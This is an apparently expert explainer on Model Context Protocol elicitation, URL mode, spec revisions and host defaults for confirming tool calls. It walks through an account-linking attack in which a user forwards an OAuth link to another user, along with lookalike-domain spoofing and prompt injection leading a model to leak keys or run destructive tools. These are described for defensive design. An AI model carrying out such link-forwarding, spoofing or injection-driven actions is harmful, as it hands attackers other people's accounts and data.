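The digest ties Sam's answer to the files in the question. If a faulty client repeated the call with a different list of paths, the digest would not match and the server would refuse it.

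How much of this happens by default depends on the developer's library. The Python SDK's main server class encrypts the string by default, adds the request details and a ten-minute limit, and includes the user's identity when it has one. The SDK's built-in method for asking questions also ties each answer to the exact wording the user saw, and asks again if the wording changes. The official Ruby SDK sends the string as written unless the developer supplies a key, according to Model Context Protocol's *Multi-Round-Trip Results*.

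Protecting `requestState` against forgery doesn't prove that Sam agreed, because a malicious client can write `accept` in `inputResponses` itself. It could even do this in the first call, before the server has asked anything. A server can prevent that by rejecting any answer that arrives without a valid `requestState`, but this only shows that the server sent the question.

### Doing the work twice

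When the second request arrives, the server runs the tool's code again from the beginning, as the Ruby guide explains, so anything the code did before asking the question happens twice. If `delete_files` emailed the team about the deletion and then asked Sam to confirm, the team would get two emails, or one about a deletion that Sam refused. Developers can avoid this by asking before the code changes anything.

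The request with the answer can also arrive twice. If the server deletes the files but the connection drops before its reply gets through, the client can't determine whether the call succeeded and may send the confirmed call again. For `delete_files` the repeat is usually harmless, because the files are already gone. But if Sam has saved a new `plan-final.txt` in the meantime, the server deletes that too, even though Sam's answer was about the old one.

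The US National Security Agency (NSA) raised the general problem shortly before the new exchange became final, in guidance that its Artificial Intelligence Security Center published on 20 May 2026 (NSA press release, 2026). *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (NSA, 2026) warns that idempotency "is not directly enforced by MCP". The guidance says that MCP leaves idempotency to JSON-RPC and message queues, so responsibility falls on the client side, where developers may handle it badly or overlook it.

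The NSA was writing about stolen sessions and replayed messages under the 2025-11-25 revision, not about elicitation. Its warning matters more under the new revision, because the client must resend a call each time the user answers a question. TinyFish, an AI company, makes this connection in its summary of the new revision: "The resume is a retry." JSON-RPC does little to help the server recognize the repeated call, because that call must have a new request ID.

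The current text gives the server more responsibility than the NSA's account suggests. The NSA recommends that messages include expiry times and data for detecting replays, and a well-protected `requestState` includes an expiry time and is tied to one request. But the maintainers warn that these measures don't guarantee single use, since a valid string can be reused until it expires. If an operation must happen at most once, the server MUST enforce that itself.

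For destructive operations, Körbächer recommends putting a one-time identifier in the string and recording its use. Every machine running the service then needs access to that record, which brings back some of the shared storage the new design was meant to avoid. The record can be small, though. With the Python SDK's default limit, a server would have to keep each identifier for only ten minutes, because after that it would reject the string as expired.

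## How a server sends the user to a web page

A server has to use URL mode instead of a form for passwords, API keys and card payments. It sends the client a web address, which the user opens in a browser to enter the information. The client has access to the address and the user's decision about whether to open it, but not to anything that happens on the page.

*URL Mode Elicitation for secure out-of-band interactions* (Barbettini and Dawson, 2025) proposed URL mode as SEP-1036, and it entered the specification with the 2025-11-25 revision. Until then, according to *One Year of MCP* (Model Context Protocol, 2025), server developers had to trust the client with users' credentials or write their own authorisation logic.

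### Why secrets bypass the client and the model

SEP-1036 covers three kinds of interaction. The simplest is collecting a credential such as an API key, a string that a service accepts as proof of the caller's identity. Anyone who has a copy can use it. If a key reached the model's context through a form, injected text might lead the model to copy the key into a later tool call.

Third-party authorisation is more complicated. Suppose a server needs to read Sam's private code on GitHub. Services like GitHub use OAuth, the standard behind pages that ask whether an app may access your account. Sam logs in on GitHub's own site and approves certain permissions, and GitHub issues a token limited to them. *URL Elicitation deep dive* (Barbettini, 2026) describes two trust boundaries, one between the client and the MCP server and another between the MCP server and GitHub. The client should have a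 token only for the MCP server.

Barbettini and Dawson reject having the client obtain the GitHub token and give it to the server. This would make the server a token passthrough, and MCP forbids a server from using the client's credentials at another service. The server also MUST NOT send the GitHub token back to the client.

If card numbers passed through the client, every chat application that supported payments would have to meet the card industry's PCI security requirements.

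URL mode hides secrets from the client and the model, but not always from the server. With OAuth, the server gets a token, not Sam's GitHub password. If Sam enters an API key instead, the server receives the key, so Sam still has to trust whoever runs the server.

Barbettini and Dawson first proposed a separate feature called `userInteraction`, according to Arcade.dev, where Barbettini works. After forms were added to the specification in June 2025, they turned their proposal into a second mode of elicitation, because two similar features for asking users questions would have been confusing.

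### Entering an API key

Suppose Sam asks for an hourly forecast, which the weather server buys from a provider that requires each customer's own API key. The client's request has to declare `"elicitation": { "url": {} }`. The server has no key on file for Sam, so it returns an input-required result. The result below follows an example in Model Context Protocol's *Elicitation*, with a different address and message:

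```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 21,
  "result": {
    "resultType": "input_required",
    "inputRequests": {
      "provider_key": {
        "method": "elicitation/create",
        "params": {
          "mode": "url",
          "url": "https://weather.example/add-key",
          "message": "Hourly forecasts need a key from our data provider. Add yours on this page."
        }
      }
    },
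    "requestState": "opaque-protected-string"
  }
}
```

The host might show Sam this:

```text
weather wants to open a web page:
"Hourly forecasts need a key from our data provider. Add yours on this page."

https://weather.example/add-key
Website: weather.example

[Open page]  [Decline]  [Cancel]
```

The rest of the exchange happens in two places:

1. Sam clicks "Open page", and the host opens the address in a browser.
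2. The client repeats the tool call with `{"action": "accept"}` as the answer. Unlike the answer to a form, this has no `content`.
3. In the browser, the server checks that the visitor is Sam. Sam types the key, and the server stores it under Sam's identity.
4. The server uses the key to fetch the forecast, and returns it as the result of the repeated call.

Later calls can use the stored key, so Sam has to do this only once.

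The client may complete step 2 before Sam has typed anything, because `accept` means only that Sam agreed to open the page. So the server has to check its own records for the key when the repeated call arrives. If the key is missing, the server can hold the call open for a while or return another input-required result. Holding it open works badly for slow tasks because, as Barbettini and Dawson point out, users may take minutes to finish a payment or abandon it.

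If the server returns the same question again, the host could prompt Sam a second time while Sam is still looking for the key. The Model Context Protocol specification's rules on multi-round-trip requests allow the server to return `requestState` with no questions instead, and the client may then retry without asking the user anything. A client that retries too quickly could still reach the Python SDK's default limit of ten rounds before Sam finds the key.

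Mistaking consent for completion is more serious when money is involved. In an example from Model Context Protocol's *Elicitation* guide for the Python SDK, a restaurant's MCP server asks for a 20-euro deposit. After an `accept`, the tool only tells the user to complete the payment in the browser, and a separate tool records the deposit once the payment provider reports it. If the server confirmed the booking on `accept`, a user could open the payment page, close it without paying, and still get the table.

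Clients don't all send `accept` at the same moment. The sample client in the Amazon Web Services guide *Use elicitation with your AgentCore gateway* waits until the user presses Enter to report having finished. The server still has only the user's report that they finished.

The 2025-11-25 revision let a server notify the client when the user had finished, but the maintainers have since removed that message, according to the Model Context Protocol changelog. A client now learns the outcome by retrying, so it SHOULD let the user retry or cancel the call manually.

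### What the client has to show

The Model Context Protocol page sets out these duties for a client that receives a URL:

| Strength | Duty |
| --- | --- |
| MUST | "show the full URL to the user for examination before consent" |
| MUST | "clearly display the target domain/host" before navigation |
| MUST NOT | "open the URL without explicit consent from the user" |
| MUST NOT | "automatically pre-fetch the URL or any of its metadata" |
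| MUST | Open the URL in a way that doesn't let the client or model "inspect the content or user inputs" |
| SHOULD | "highlight the domain of the URL to mitigate subdomain spoofing" |
| SHOULD | "have warnings for ambiguous/suspicious URIs", such as those containing Punycode |
| SHOULD NOT | Make URLs clickable in any field of an elicitation except `url` |

Clients must show the domain, and the protocol recommends that they also emphasise it within the address. The emphasis helps because a full address can mislead people who read only its beginning. For example, `https://weather.example.account-check.example/add-key` starts like the weather server's address but belongs to `account-check.example`. OAuth addresses can also be very long, with several lines of parameters after the domain.

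Punycode is a way of writing non-Latin characters in domain names. For example, the domain `xn--pple-43d.com` can look like `apple.com`, with a Cyrillic letter in place of the "a". Even a careful reader could miss the difference without a warning.

The ban on pre-fetching means that a host can't load a page in the background to show a preview. A dishonest server could use such a preview to make the host contact an address before the user has agreed to anything. SEP-1036 mentions server-side request forgery, in which an attacker gets someone else's program to request an address the attacker can't reach, such as a page inside a company's network. But without loading the page, the host can't find out whether it redirects elsewhere, so the user approves only the first address.

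The maintainers give an example of a secure browser surface from Apple's iOS. `SFSafariViewController` is acceptable because the app can't see into the page it displays, but `WKWebView` isn't, because the app can read and change the page. The rule should also matter to hosts whose models can operate the user's browser or take screenshots, because opening the page in an ordinary browser wouldn't keep Sam's key from such a model unless the host first suspended the model's access.

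Because the client sees the page's address, a server MUST NOT put credentials or personal data in it. The server also MUST NOT send a link that opens a protected resource without a login, since a malicious client could use the link to impersonate the user. Servers SHOULD use HTTPS outside development, a weaker rule than the one in SEP-1036's security notes, which allow only HTTPS addresses.

Sample code doesn't always follow the client rules. The AWS client prints the server's message but not the address, and opens the browser without asking. The Python SDK's sample prints the address and then returns `accept` without waiting for a reply. Both are short demonstrations, but a developer who copied either into a real host would break at least one MUST rule.

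### Why the rules are more exact than those for tool inputs

Under the specification, a client MUST show a URL in full, whereas it SHOULD show tool inputs, with no requirement for how completely. The specification even names an iOS component for displaying the page. Barbettini and Dawson don't compare the two rules, but parts of their rationale help explain the difference.

The rules about where a URL can appear are meant to be predictable, so that client developers can build their interfaces around them. If a real link can appear only in the `url` field, a host can show the same careful dialog for every link and leave addresses elsewhere as plain text. The client's only responsibility is to give the user context about the address, because it has no access to what happens after that. With a tool call, the host can at least inspect the result afterwards.

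The display of URLs is also easier to regulate than the display of tool inputs. A URL is a single line with a known structure, and browser makers have dealt with lookalike domains for decades. A tool's input might be a city, a database query or a thirty-page message, so nobody could write an equally detailed display rule for all of them. That doesn't explain why only URLs must be shown in full before the user consents, so that Sam is entitled to see every character of a link to a settings page but not the path of the tax return attached to an email.

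The rule on clickable links was originally stricter. Barbettini's pull request (nbarbettini, 2025) stated that URLs MUST NOT appear in any other field of an elicitation. A reviewer, pcarleton, objected that clients enforcing this would reject legitimate questions. For example, an email server might ask the user to edit a draft that contains links, and a research tool might list the pages it had searched. Barbettini agreed that the aim was only to stop clients from making such URLs clickable, and the current rule therefore uses SHOULD NOT.

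The Agent Client Protocol, a standard separate from MCP, has since adopted almost the same requirements. Clients must show the full URL, get consent before opening it and keep the page hidden from the model. The protocol's maintainers declared the feature stable on 24 July 2026 (Agent Client Protocol, 2026).

### When one user passes the link to another

The display rules protect the person using the client. The maintainers also describe an attack in which that person is the attacker:

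1. Alice, a malicious user of an honest server, calls a tool that needs access to a GitHub account.
2. The server returns a link for authorising that access, and Alice's client displays it.
3. Instead of opening the link, Alice sends it to Bob, who uses the same server, perhaps with a note asking Bob to reconnect his account.
4. Bob opens it, recognises the server and approves access on GitHub's real site.
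5. GitHub reports the approval to the server, which assumes that it belongs to Alice's request and stores Bob's token under Alice's identity.

Alice's assistant can now use Bob's GitHub account. The same trick would work with the API-key page if Bob typed in a key and the server saved it for Alice.

The protections on `requestState` don't prevent this. The string correctly identifies Alice, and her own client returns it unchanged, so it passes every check. The mix-up happens in the browser, where the server has to identify the visitor.

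The server therefore MUST verify that the person who opens the link is the one whose request produced it. In the maintainers' example, the link leads to a "connect" page on the server's website, where the server reads the visitor's login cookie and checks whether it belongs to the user who made the tool call. If Alice made the call but the cookie is Bob's, the server stops. If the users match, it redirects the visitor to the other service's authorisation page.

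The check also has to work if an attacker edits the link. If a server put the expected user's name in the address as plain text, Alice could replace it with Bob's before forwarding the link. Servers without a website must meet the same requirement, although the maintainers don't prescribe a method for doing so.

SEP-1036 asks servers to verify the user's identity at both the beginning and the end of the process. If a server checked only at the beginning, Alice could open the connect page, pass the check, copy the address of the GitHub page that follows and send it to Bob.

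AWS's *OAuth 2.0 authorization URL session binding* describes a check at the end of authorization for AI agents built on Amazon's AgentCore platform. After the user approves access, AWS sends the browser to a page run by the agent's developer. That page has to identify the user from the browser's current session, not from a remote store of sessions. The developer's application tells AWS to fetch the token only if this is the user who started the request. AWS justifies the check by saying that a user may accidentally send the authorization link to somebody else. Each link also expires after ten minutes.

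### What the client's display can do about it

The client's display does almost nothing to stop Alice. Showing the full URL gives Alice the link to forward, and Alice could write a client that ignores every display rule. Bob opens the link from an email or a chat and so never sees a consent prompt from a host. Highlighting the domain wouldn't help Bob, because the server and GitHub are both genuine.

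The display helps against a dishonest server that links to a lookalike site, if the user knows which domain to expect. It can't protect Sam from a page on the server's real domain that collects keys and misuses them. A host could also add a line telling users not to forward the link, which might prevent the accidents AWS describes.

Some hosts can't display the link. AWS's *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Identity now offers a managed consent portal* (September 2026) announced a website for people who use agents in code editors, which AWS says can't natively present OAuth consent links or complete the identity check. Administrators can send the portal's address to their teams, who give consent before starting work. This is practical for those editors, but it may also get people used to approving access through links from colleagues and so make Alice's message to Bob look more ordinary.

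## How the duties changed from revision to revision

The duty to show a full URL dates from November 2025, when URL mode entered the specification. The clauses on confirming tool calls have kept the same wording since the first revision, a year earlier. The table gives the force of each duty in all five revisions. "Absent" means that a revision has no such clause, usually because the feature did not exist yet.

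| Duty | 2024-11-05 | 2025-03-26 | 2025-06-18 | 2025-11-25 | 2026-07-28 |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Consent before any tool runs | lower-case must | lower-case must | lower-case must | lower-case must | lower-case must |
| Human able to deny calls | SHOULD | SHOULD | SHOULD | SHOULD | SHOULD |
| Showing tool inputs | SHOULD | SHOULD | SHOULD | SHOULD | SHOULD |
| Confirming sensitive operations | SHOULD | SHOULD | SHOULD | SHOULD | SHOULD |
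| Status of annotations: untrusted unless the server is trusted | Absent | MUST | MUST | MUST | MUST |
| Identifying the server that asks | Absent | Absent | SHOULD | MUST | MUST |
| Reviewing answers before they go to the server | Absent | Absent | SHOULD | MUST, for forms | MUST, for forms |
| Requests for credentials | Absent | Absent | MUST NOT, with all other sensitive information | MUST NOT in forms; MUST use URL mode | MUST NOT in forms; MUST use URL mode |
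| Displaying URLs in full before consent | Absent | Absent | Absent | MUST | MUST |
| When a server may ask: only while handling a client's request | Absent | Absent | SHOULD, in part | SHOULD, in part | MUST |

The first row comes from the overview page. "In part" in the last row means the recommendation covered only one of the two channels a server could use over HTTP.

### Tool calls: the same words since 2024

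On the 2024-11-05 *Tools* page, the Model Context Protocol maintainers already recommended a human in the loop who can deny tool calls. They also wrote that clients SHOULD confirm sensitive operations and show tool inputs. The 2026-07-28 page, almost 21 months later, has the same sentences. Its list of security duties for clients has one more item, on references inside JSON schemas.

Some of the many changes to the rest of the page affect what a confirmation prompt has to do. Since 2025-06-18, a server can give a tool a display title outside its annotations, and since 2025-11-25 it can add an icon. The rule on untrusted annotations does not mention either field, although both may appear in a prompt. The Model Context Protocol's current base protocol *Overview* separately tells clients to treat icons as untrusted, but there is no such rule for the top-level title.

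The 2026-07-28 revision also introduced `x-mcp-header`, which exposes some arguments to proxies, but it did not change the client's duty to show inputs. It added advice on distinguishing identically named tools from different servers, which should help hosts label their prompts correctly.

### March 2025: annotations and the untrusted rule

The Model Context Protocol changelog for 2025-03-26 lists tool annotations as a major change and links to pull request 185. In the 2024-11-05 revision, a tool's definition has only a name, a description and an input schema. The *Tools* page for 2025-03-26 adds `annotations` and the rule that clients MUST consider them untrusted unless they come from trusted servers.

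Several third-party pages give a different date, possibly because MCP has another field called `annotations`, which describes the intended audience and priority of content such as text or images. The *Tools* page first mentions that field in the 2025-06-18 revision, so a search for the word could easily lead to the wrong revision.

The Model Context Protocol overview for 2024-11-05 says only that tools represent arbitrary code execution and call for caution. In the 2025-03-26 overview, the maintainers added a matching line that descriptions of tool behaviour "should be considered untrusted" (copy hosted by Glama, 2025). Neither that line nor the capitalised rule has changed since.

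The new rule was a MUST, stronger than the confirmation clauses it was meant to support, which were SHOULDs. A host that ignores annotations and never asks the user anything satisfies the MUST, because it trusts no annotation, and departs only from the SHOULDs. The rule prevents a false hint from removing a prompt only in hosts that show prompts.

### June 2025: elicitation begins at SHOULD

The 2025-06-18 revision added elicitation through pull request 382, according to the Model Context Protocol changelog. The Model Context Protocol *Elicitation* page warned that the design might change. Applications SHOULD make clear which server was asking, let users review and change their answers, and offer clear ways to decline and cancel.

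A list at the end of the page added more duties for clients, also at the SHOULD level. Clients were to have approval controls, limit the rate of requests, explain what information the server was requesting and why, and let users decline at any time. Both clients and servers were to check answers against the form's schema.

The only MUST NOT about the content of a question barred servers from requesting "sensitive information", a term the maintainers did not define. Their example on the same page is a request for a name, an email address and an age, so they can't have meant all personal data. The term surely covered passwords and API keys, and since URL mode did not exist yet, servers had no permitted way to request them through elicitation.

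### November 2025: the same duties at MUST

In the 2025-11-25 revision, the maintainers changed "Applications SHOULD" to "MCP clients MUST" above the three main duties. The revision requires the review of answers only for forms, because the client never sees the answers in URL mode. It also added mandatory rules for how clients display URLs, and it required servers to bind each request to the identity of the client and the user.

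In the security list, the item on identifying the server rose to MUST, but the items on approval controls, declining at any time, explaining the request and rate limiting stayed at SHOULD. Oddly, a client MUST provide clear options to decline and cancel, but only SHOULD let the user decline "at any time". Perhaps the weaker clause covers a user who changes their mind after the first of several questions, but the maintainers don't explain the difference.

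The November revision also narrowed the ban on requesting sensitive information. The term now means secrets and credentials that "grant access or authorize transactions", and servers may not request these in a form. This mostly confirmed what the old example implied about names and email addresses, but it may have loosened the rule for other private facts. A health server that asked for a user's diagnosis in a form would probably have broken the June rule, but the November text allows this if the user can review the answer and decline.

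Another change made careless answers easier. In the published June schema, only true-or-false fields could have a default. Under the November revision, every type of field can have one, and clients that support defaults SHOULD pre-fill fields with them. The revision also introduced lists that let users select several options.

The Model Context Protocol changelog for this revision mentions URL mode, defaults and the new lists, but not the change from SHOULD to MUST. The omission is surprising because the previous changelog included a similar change, to the rules for operating a connection, among its major items. A developer who relied on the changelog to update a client could have missed three new requirements.

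### July 2026: when a server may ask

The newest revision kept the main client duties for elicitation at MUST but changed how a server asks for input. The server now puts its question in an input-required result and can no longer send its own request.

In their release candidate post, the Model Context Protocol maintainers write that earlier versions recommended asking only during a client's request. This is only partly true. SEP-2260, the Model Context Protocol proposal behind the new rule, quotes the 2025-11-25 text for HTTP, which gave servers two channels:

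- On the stream that answered a client's request, the server's messages SHOULD relate to that request.
- On an optional stream that the client opened separately, they SHOULD be "unrelated to any concurrently-running JSON-RPC" request.

A server that used the second channel could therefore follow the recommendation and still question a user who had not started anything. The proposal responds that the maintainers had always intended questions to be asked during other operations, and that server developers could not rely on the second channel because clients did not have to open it.

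The working group considered softer rules but rejected SHOULD NOT because the remaining ambiguity would have prevented simpler connections. It also rejected a flag that would let clients permit unprompted requests, because it knew of no demand for such requests.

Several duties disappeared when the features they governed were removed. In the 2025-11-25 revision, a URL request had an `elicitationId`, and the server could later send a notice that the user had finished on the web page. The revision required clients to ignore notices with unknown IDs and servers to send each notice only to the client concerned. According to the Model Context Protocol changelog, the maintainers removed both the ID and the notice because clients now retry instead, and a server that still needs an identifier puts its own in `requestState`. Removing these requirements did not weaken the user's position, because the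 notice never conveyed the user's consent.

The overview for 2024-11-05 and the one for 2025-11-25, Model Context Protocol's *Specification* (2025), both include the principle that "Users must explicitly approve any LLM sampling requests". The draft overview omits this principle. The maintainers have deprecated sampling, but it remains for now.

### The missing recommendation on rate limits

"Clients SHOULD implement rate limiting" appears in the elicitation security lists for 2025-06-18 and 2025-11-25. It is missing from the page for the current revision, 2026-07-28, and the changelog does not mention the removal.

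The new exchange may explain this. A server that could send questions at any time might have flooded the user with them, and a limit in the client was an obvious defence. Now the server sends questions only in reply to the client's requests, so a client that makes fewer requests will also receive fewer questions.

This is not a complete substitute, because the protocol's rules for the exchange do not limit the number of questions in one result or the number of rounds. The *Tools* page still requires servers to limit the rate of tool calls, but a developer who builds a server to pester the user has no reason to comply. Host developers would be wise to keep the limit they had.

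### Why elicitation hardened and tool confirmation did not

The contrast in the table holds, but the elicitation duties did not all change in the same direction. The June 2025 page had eight duties for clients, not counting duplicates. Three are now MUST, four are still SHOULD and one is gone. The ban on sensitive information became narrower. The maintainers do bind clients on the *Tools* page, where the annotation rule has been a MUST from the start.

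No changelog mentions how binding the tool-confirmation clauses are, and the maintainers don't explain on the specification pages why they left them at SHOULD. The maintainers do explain some of the changes to elicitation. SEP-2260 cites simpler connections, clearer context for users and a smaller security risk. According to its proposal, URL mode exists to keep credentials and payments away from the client. None of these reasons explains why clients must now identify the server above an ordinary form, so any explanation of that change, or of why the tool clauses stayed at SHOULD, is inference.

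The maintainers say on both pages that MCP "does not mandate any specific user interaction model", but on the *Elicitation* page they also require an interface that identifies the server. An outsider can't verify either that interface or a confirmation prompt from the protocol messages, so the difficulty of checking can't be the whole explanation.

A better explanation is that the elicitation duties are easier to meet. Elicitation makes little sense without someone to answer, so a client that supports it normally already has a screen and a user. Showing the server's name and adding a review step takes little extra work. Tool calls, however, can run without anyone watching. If "confirmation" meant a prompt for each call, a MUST on confirming them would put every unattended agent in breach, along with every host that lets users approve calls in advance.

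Timing probably mattered as well. Elicitation was five months old when its duties became stricter, and the maintainers had warned developers on its page to expect changes. By then, developers had been building hosts around the tool clauses for a year. Forbidding unprompted questions also let the maintainers simplify the connection between client and server, whereas requiring a confirmation prompt would not have simplified anything.

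The tool clauses have stayed the same, word for word, through a complete redesign of the protocol. The maintainers may have reconsidered them each time and been satisfied, or nobody may have proposed a change. The burden of prompting could explain why the maintainers would not require a prompt for every call, but not why a host that does show a prompt may leave out the inputs. A MUST that applied only when a host shows a prompt would not affect unattended agents.

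### What an application built to an older revision still owes

Past revisions are final, so later changes do not add requirements to software that still uses an older one. The revision that the client and server use between them decides which text applies:

- **2024-11-05:** A host owes the SHOULDs on tool calls and the overview's lower-case duty of consent. It has no rule on annotations.
- **2025-03-26:** The host must also treat annotations as untrusted, unless the server is trusted.
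- **2025-06-18:** If the host supports elicitation, it SHOULD identify the server, offer a review and limit the rate of questions. Servers may not request any sensitive information.
- **2025-11-25:** Identifying the server, offering a review and providing ways to decline become MUSTs. Rate limiting is still a SHOULD, and a host that supports URL mode owes all the display duties for links.

A client can become non-compliant by adopting a newer revision, even if its interface stays the same. For example, under the June 2025 text, a client could show forms without identifying the server if its developers had a considered reason. The November revision makes identifying the server a MUST, so a client that adopts it and keeps the same forms violates the specification.

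An older client also limits what a newer server can request. A client built to the 2025-06-18 revision declares elicitation with an empty object, which under later revisions means that it supports only forms. A server that needs an API key can't request it from this client through a form, because the key is a secret, or through a URL, because the client hasn't declared that mode. The server has to get the key another way, such as through its own settings page.

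Many hosts will need to support both old and new servers for some time. The documentation for the protocol's official Ruby SDK describes both the old and new ways of asking the user a question. Results from older servers have no `resultType`, and a current client MUST treat them as complete.

If a host like this applied each revision's display rules separately, a dishonest server could offer only 2025-06-18 so that the client's weaker duties applied. The host can avoid this by identifying the server and letting the user review answers under every revision. The older revisions don't prohibit this, and the developers have to build those screens for the current revision anyway.

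Removing sampling would take a separate proposal. As long as a host offers it, users should still be able to review the server's prompts and the model's replies.

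## How hosts decide when to ask, and what happens by default

The clauses on confirming tool calls have been recommendations (SHOULD) since 2024, so each host's developers decide which calls to run immediately, which to hold for the user's approval and which to refuse. They can base that decision on the server's hints, evidence that the server is trustworthy, and settings chosen by the user or an administrator. Most of the open-source hosts that researchers have examined use none of these by default and run the call without asking.

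### From hints to a decision

The MCP specification does not define how to combine this information, but the table below is consistent with its cautious defaults and its rule on untrusted annotations. A host uses the first row that applies.

| Situation | Trusted server | Unknown server |
| --- | --- | --- |
| The user or an administrator has blocked the tool | Refuse | Refuse |
| The user has approved the tool in advance, and its definition is still the same | Allow | Allow |
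| The server declares the tool read-only | Allow | Ask |
| Anything else, including a tool with no hints | Ask | Ask |

If the result is "ask" and nobody is there to answer, the host should refuse.

Suppose the model proposes a call to `purge_orders`, which permanently deletes every order from before 2026. The tool might be on a server run by the company, whose engineers review the tool's annotations, or on a server the user found in a public catalogue yesterday. The user has neither approved nor blocked the tool.

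| Server's declaration | Company's server | Catalogue server |
| --- | --- | --- |
| `destructiveHint: true` | Ask | Ask |
| No hints | Ask | Ask |
| `readOnlyHint: true`, by mistake or dishonestly | Allow, and the orders are lost | Ask |

Trust in the server matters only when the hint wrongly marks the deletion as safe, so the one bad outcome comes from a mistake that the company's engineers missed. The user's settings can override this. If the user clicked "Always allow" last week, either server can delete the orders without a prompt.

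A less cautious host could add a row that lets trusted servers make non-destructive changes without asking. That row would cover creating a draft, but it could also cover sending an email, because a developer can call that additive under MCP's definition.

### How four hosts use the hints

Codex relies on hints more than most hosts. Yao and colleagues read its source code and found that the command-line version asks for approval before a call unless the tool is not destructive and is either read-only or closed-world. It therefore asks before calling a tool with no hints. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, a destructive hint always requires approval, even on a tool that also has a read-only hint, where the MCP schema gives the destructive hint no meaning.

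The default rule lets a closed-world tool add records without a prompt. Users who want to review such changes can choose a mode that OpenAI merged on 7 July 2026. *The Writes Mode* (Vaughan, 2026) says this mode runs tools that declare themselves read-only and asks before running any others.

Codex users can also block tools by category. Setting `destructive_enabled = false` for an app blocks all of its tools that have a destructive hint, according to *MCP Tool Annotations as Risk Vocabulary*. A tool wrongly marked as read-only is not blocked. Codex can also remember an approval for the rest of a session. It stores the approval under the server, connector and tool name but not the arguments, so approval to delete one record would also cover the next deletion with that tool.

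According to OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT*, users have up to four settings for connected apps: always ask, allow reads, allow low-risk actions or allow everything. The low-risk setting applies when no other policy overrides it, so it appears to be the default. Under that setting, ChatGPT may ask about a higher-risk action or refuse it without asking. OpenAI says actions such as sending messages, deleting records and sharing health information may need more review.

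According to OpenAI's *ChatGPT Developer mode*, when developers connect their own servers to ChatGPT, write actions need confirmation by default, and any tool without `readOnlyHint` counts as a write. Users can have ChatGPT remember their choice for a tool, but only within that conversation.

A read-only hint doesn't guarantee that ChatGPT will skip the confirmation prompt. In *Action Confirmation for Read only tool*, a thread on OpenAI's forum, a developer asks why ChatGPT requests confirmation on every call to an app whose tools are all read-only. Someone apparently from OpenAI replies that a model uses the whole conversation to decide when to ask, because read tools can still leak data to servers. This would catch the weather lookup that mentions an oncology clinic, which a rule based only on hints would allow.

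Anthropic tells developers of Claude connectors (its name for MCP servers that users add) that hints determine automatic permissions. Read-only tools can run without confirmation for each call, and destructive tools "always prompt". Anthropic also says that organisations can set a connector's write and delete tools to Always allow, Needs approval or Blocked.

The promise about destructive tools is hard to reconcile with a newer default. In an update dated 22 October 2026, Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) announced that most Claude apps would start new sessions in auto mode on the Pro, Max and Team plans. In this mode, an automated check, rather than the user, reviews each action. Hartherz's *Claude*, a short guide to connector settings, warns that "Needs approval" amounts to permission in auto mode. If that is right, users who want to rule out a deletion should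 block the tool.

VS Code asks before ordinary MCP calls but skips tools with a read-only hint and servers that run in a sandbox, as Yao and colleagues found in its source code. The four hosts compare as follows when the user has to approve calls and has not changed the settings for a particular tool:

| Host | Read-only hint | No hints | Destructive hint |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Codex CLI | Runs, unless also destructive | Asks | Asks |
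| ChatGPT, developer mode | Counts as a read, but may still ask | Asks | Asks |
| Claude connectors | Can run | Not specified | Asks |
| VS Code | Runs | Asks | Asks |

These rules mostly depend on what the tool declares, regardless of who runs the server. Anthropic's developer platform also lets developers account for trust. By default, it asks for approval before running tools from MCP servers but runs its built-in tools without asking. Anthropic explains that this default prevents tools that a server adds later from running without approval. Developers can turn off the prompts for a server they trust.

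### Directories that require hints

Both OpenAI and Anthropic require annotations from servers in their public directories. OpenAI's *Plugin guidelines* require every tool to set `readOnlyHint`, `destructiveHint` and `openWorldHint` explicitly to true or false. Anthropic requires all applicable annotations, in particular `readOnlyHint`, `destructiveHint` and `title`. According to Anthropic, missing annotations are the most common problem with submissions and account for 30% of rejections.

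OpenAI's directory rules are stricter about reversible changes than its guide to building servers. Under the plugin guidelines, developers should label a tool that overwrites data as destructive, and the ability to undo the change is not enough to justify `destructiveHint: false`. A document service that keeps every past version of a file should still label its overwrite tool destructive.

Reviewers can catch labels that are obviously wrong. According to OpenAI's *Remote MCP server review requirements*, OpenAI also periodically fetches each server's tool list after publication and compares it with the published one. If a hint changes, the old definition stays in use until the new one passes automated checks. But calls go to the developer's live server, so these checks would miss new code behind an unchanged hint.

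Anthropic scans each submission automatically and lists it as a Community connector by default. It tests every tool only if it selects the connector for Verified review. A listing is therefore some evidence that a connector's hints are right, but a Community listing is much weaker evidence than a Verified one. The tools run the same way under either label. Servers that users connect by address, outside the directories, don't have to pass either company's review.

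### What the maintainers observed in March 2026

In March 2026, the Model Context Protocol maintainers described how clients were using annotations a year after their introduction. Most clients trusted any server the user had installed. None showed annotations in approval prompts or let users filter tools by them. The closest feature in production was GitHub's read-only mode, which about 17% of users had enabled.

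The maintainers attributed the uneven use to a split among MCP's users. Developers of autonomous agents saw confirmations as friction and relied on sandboxes, while companies wanted more annotations than MCP had.

The observation about installation mostly still holds. Directory reviews and Anthropic's setting for trusted servers give hosts other reasons to trust a server, but Yao and colleagues examined 41 open-source hosts later in the year and found that 32 ran calls without an approval step once the user had added the server.

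Hosts seem to have changed how they filter tools more than what their approval prompts show. According to Hartherz, Claude's settings usually sort a connector's tools into read-only and write/delete groups, each with its own permission control. Codex can block destructive tools for individual apps. OpenAI's description of ChatGPT's approval card mentions the app and the proposed action, but not the server's hints.

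The 17% figure describes one company's users at one point in time. It doesn't show how many people elsewhere would choose a read-only mode, or how many of the other 83% considered it and decided they needed write access.

### Whether anyone asks before a destructive call

A person might see a destructive call because the host shows a prompt or because the server asks through elicitation. Earlier studies each looked at only one of these routes. Yao and colleagues examined both in November 2026 and estimated how often neither the host nor the server asks.

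In the threat model, the server and host are honest, but the model may call a destructive tool against the user's wishes because of prompt injection or a misread task. A confirmation therefore counts only if the decision comes from outside the model. An argument such as `confirm=true`, which some servers require before deleting anything, doesn't count because the model can supply it itself.

The server figures come from the same 1,000 repositories in which they had compared hints with code. These were the 200 with the most stars among 17,554 public ones in Python, TypeScript or JavaScript, and 800 others chosen at random. Of the 366 tools whose code the language models read, 269 counted as destructive. Weighted to represent the registry, and with an allowance for destructive tools that the initial search missed, the results were:

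| Strongest confirmation in the server | Share of destructive tools |
| --- | --- |
| None, and no destructive hint | 70% |
| A destructive hint only | 20% |
| A flag or token that the model can supply | 8.9% |
| A question to the user, but the tool runs if the host can't relay it | 0.2% |
| Refusal unless a person has answered | 0.5% |

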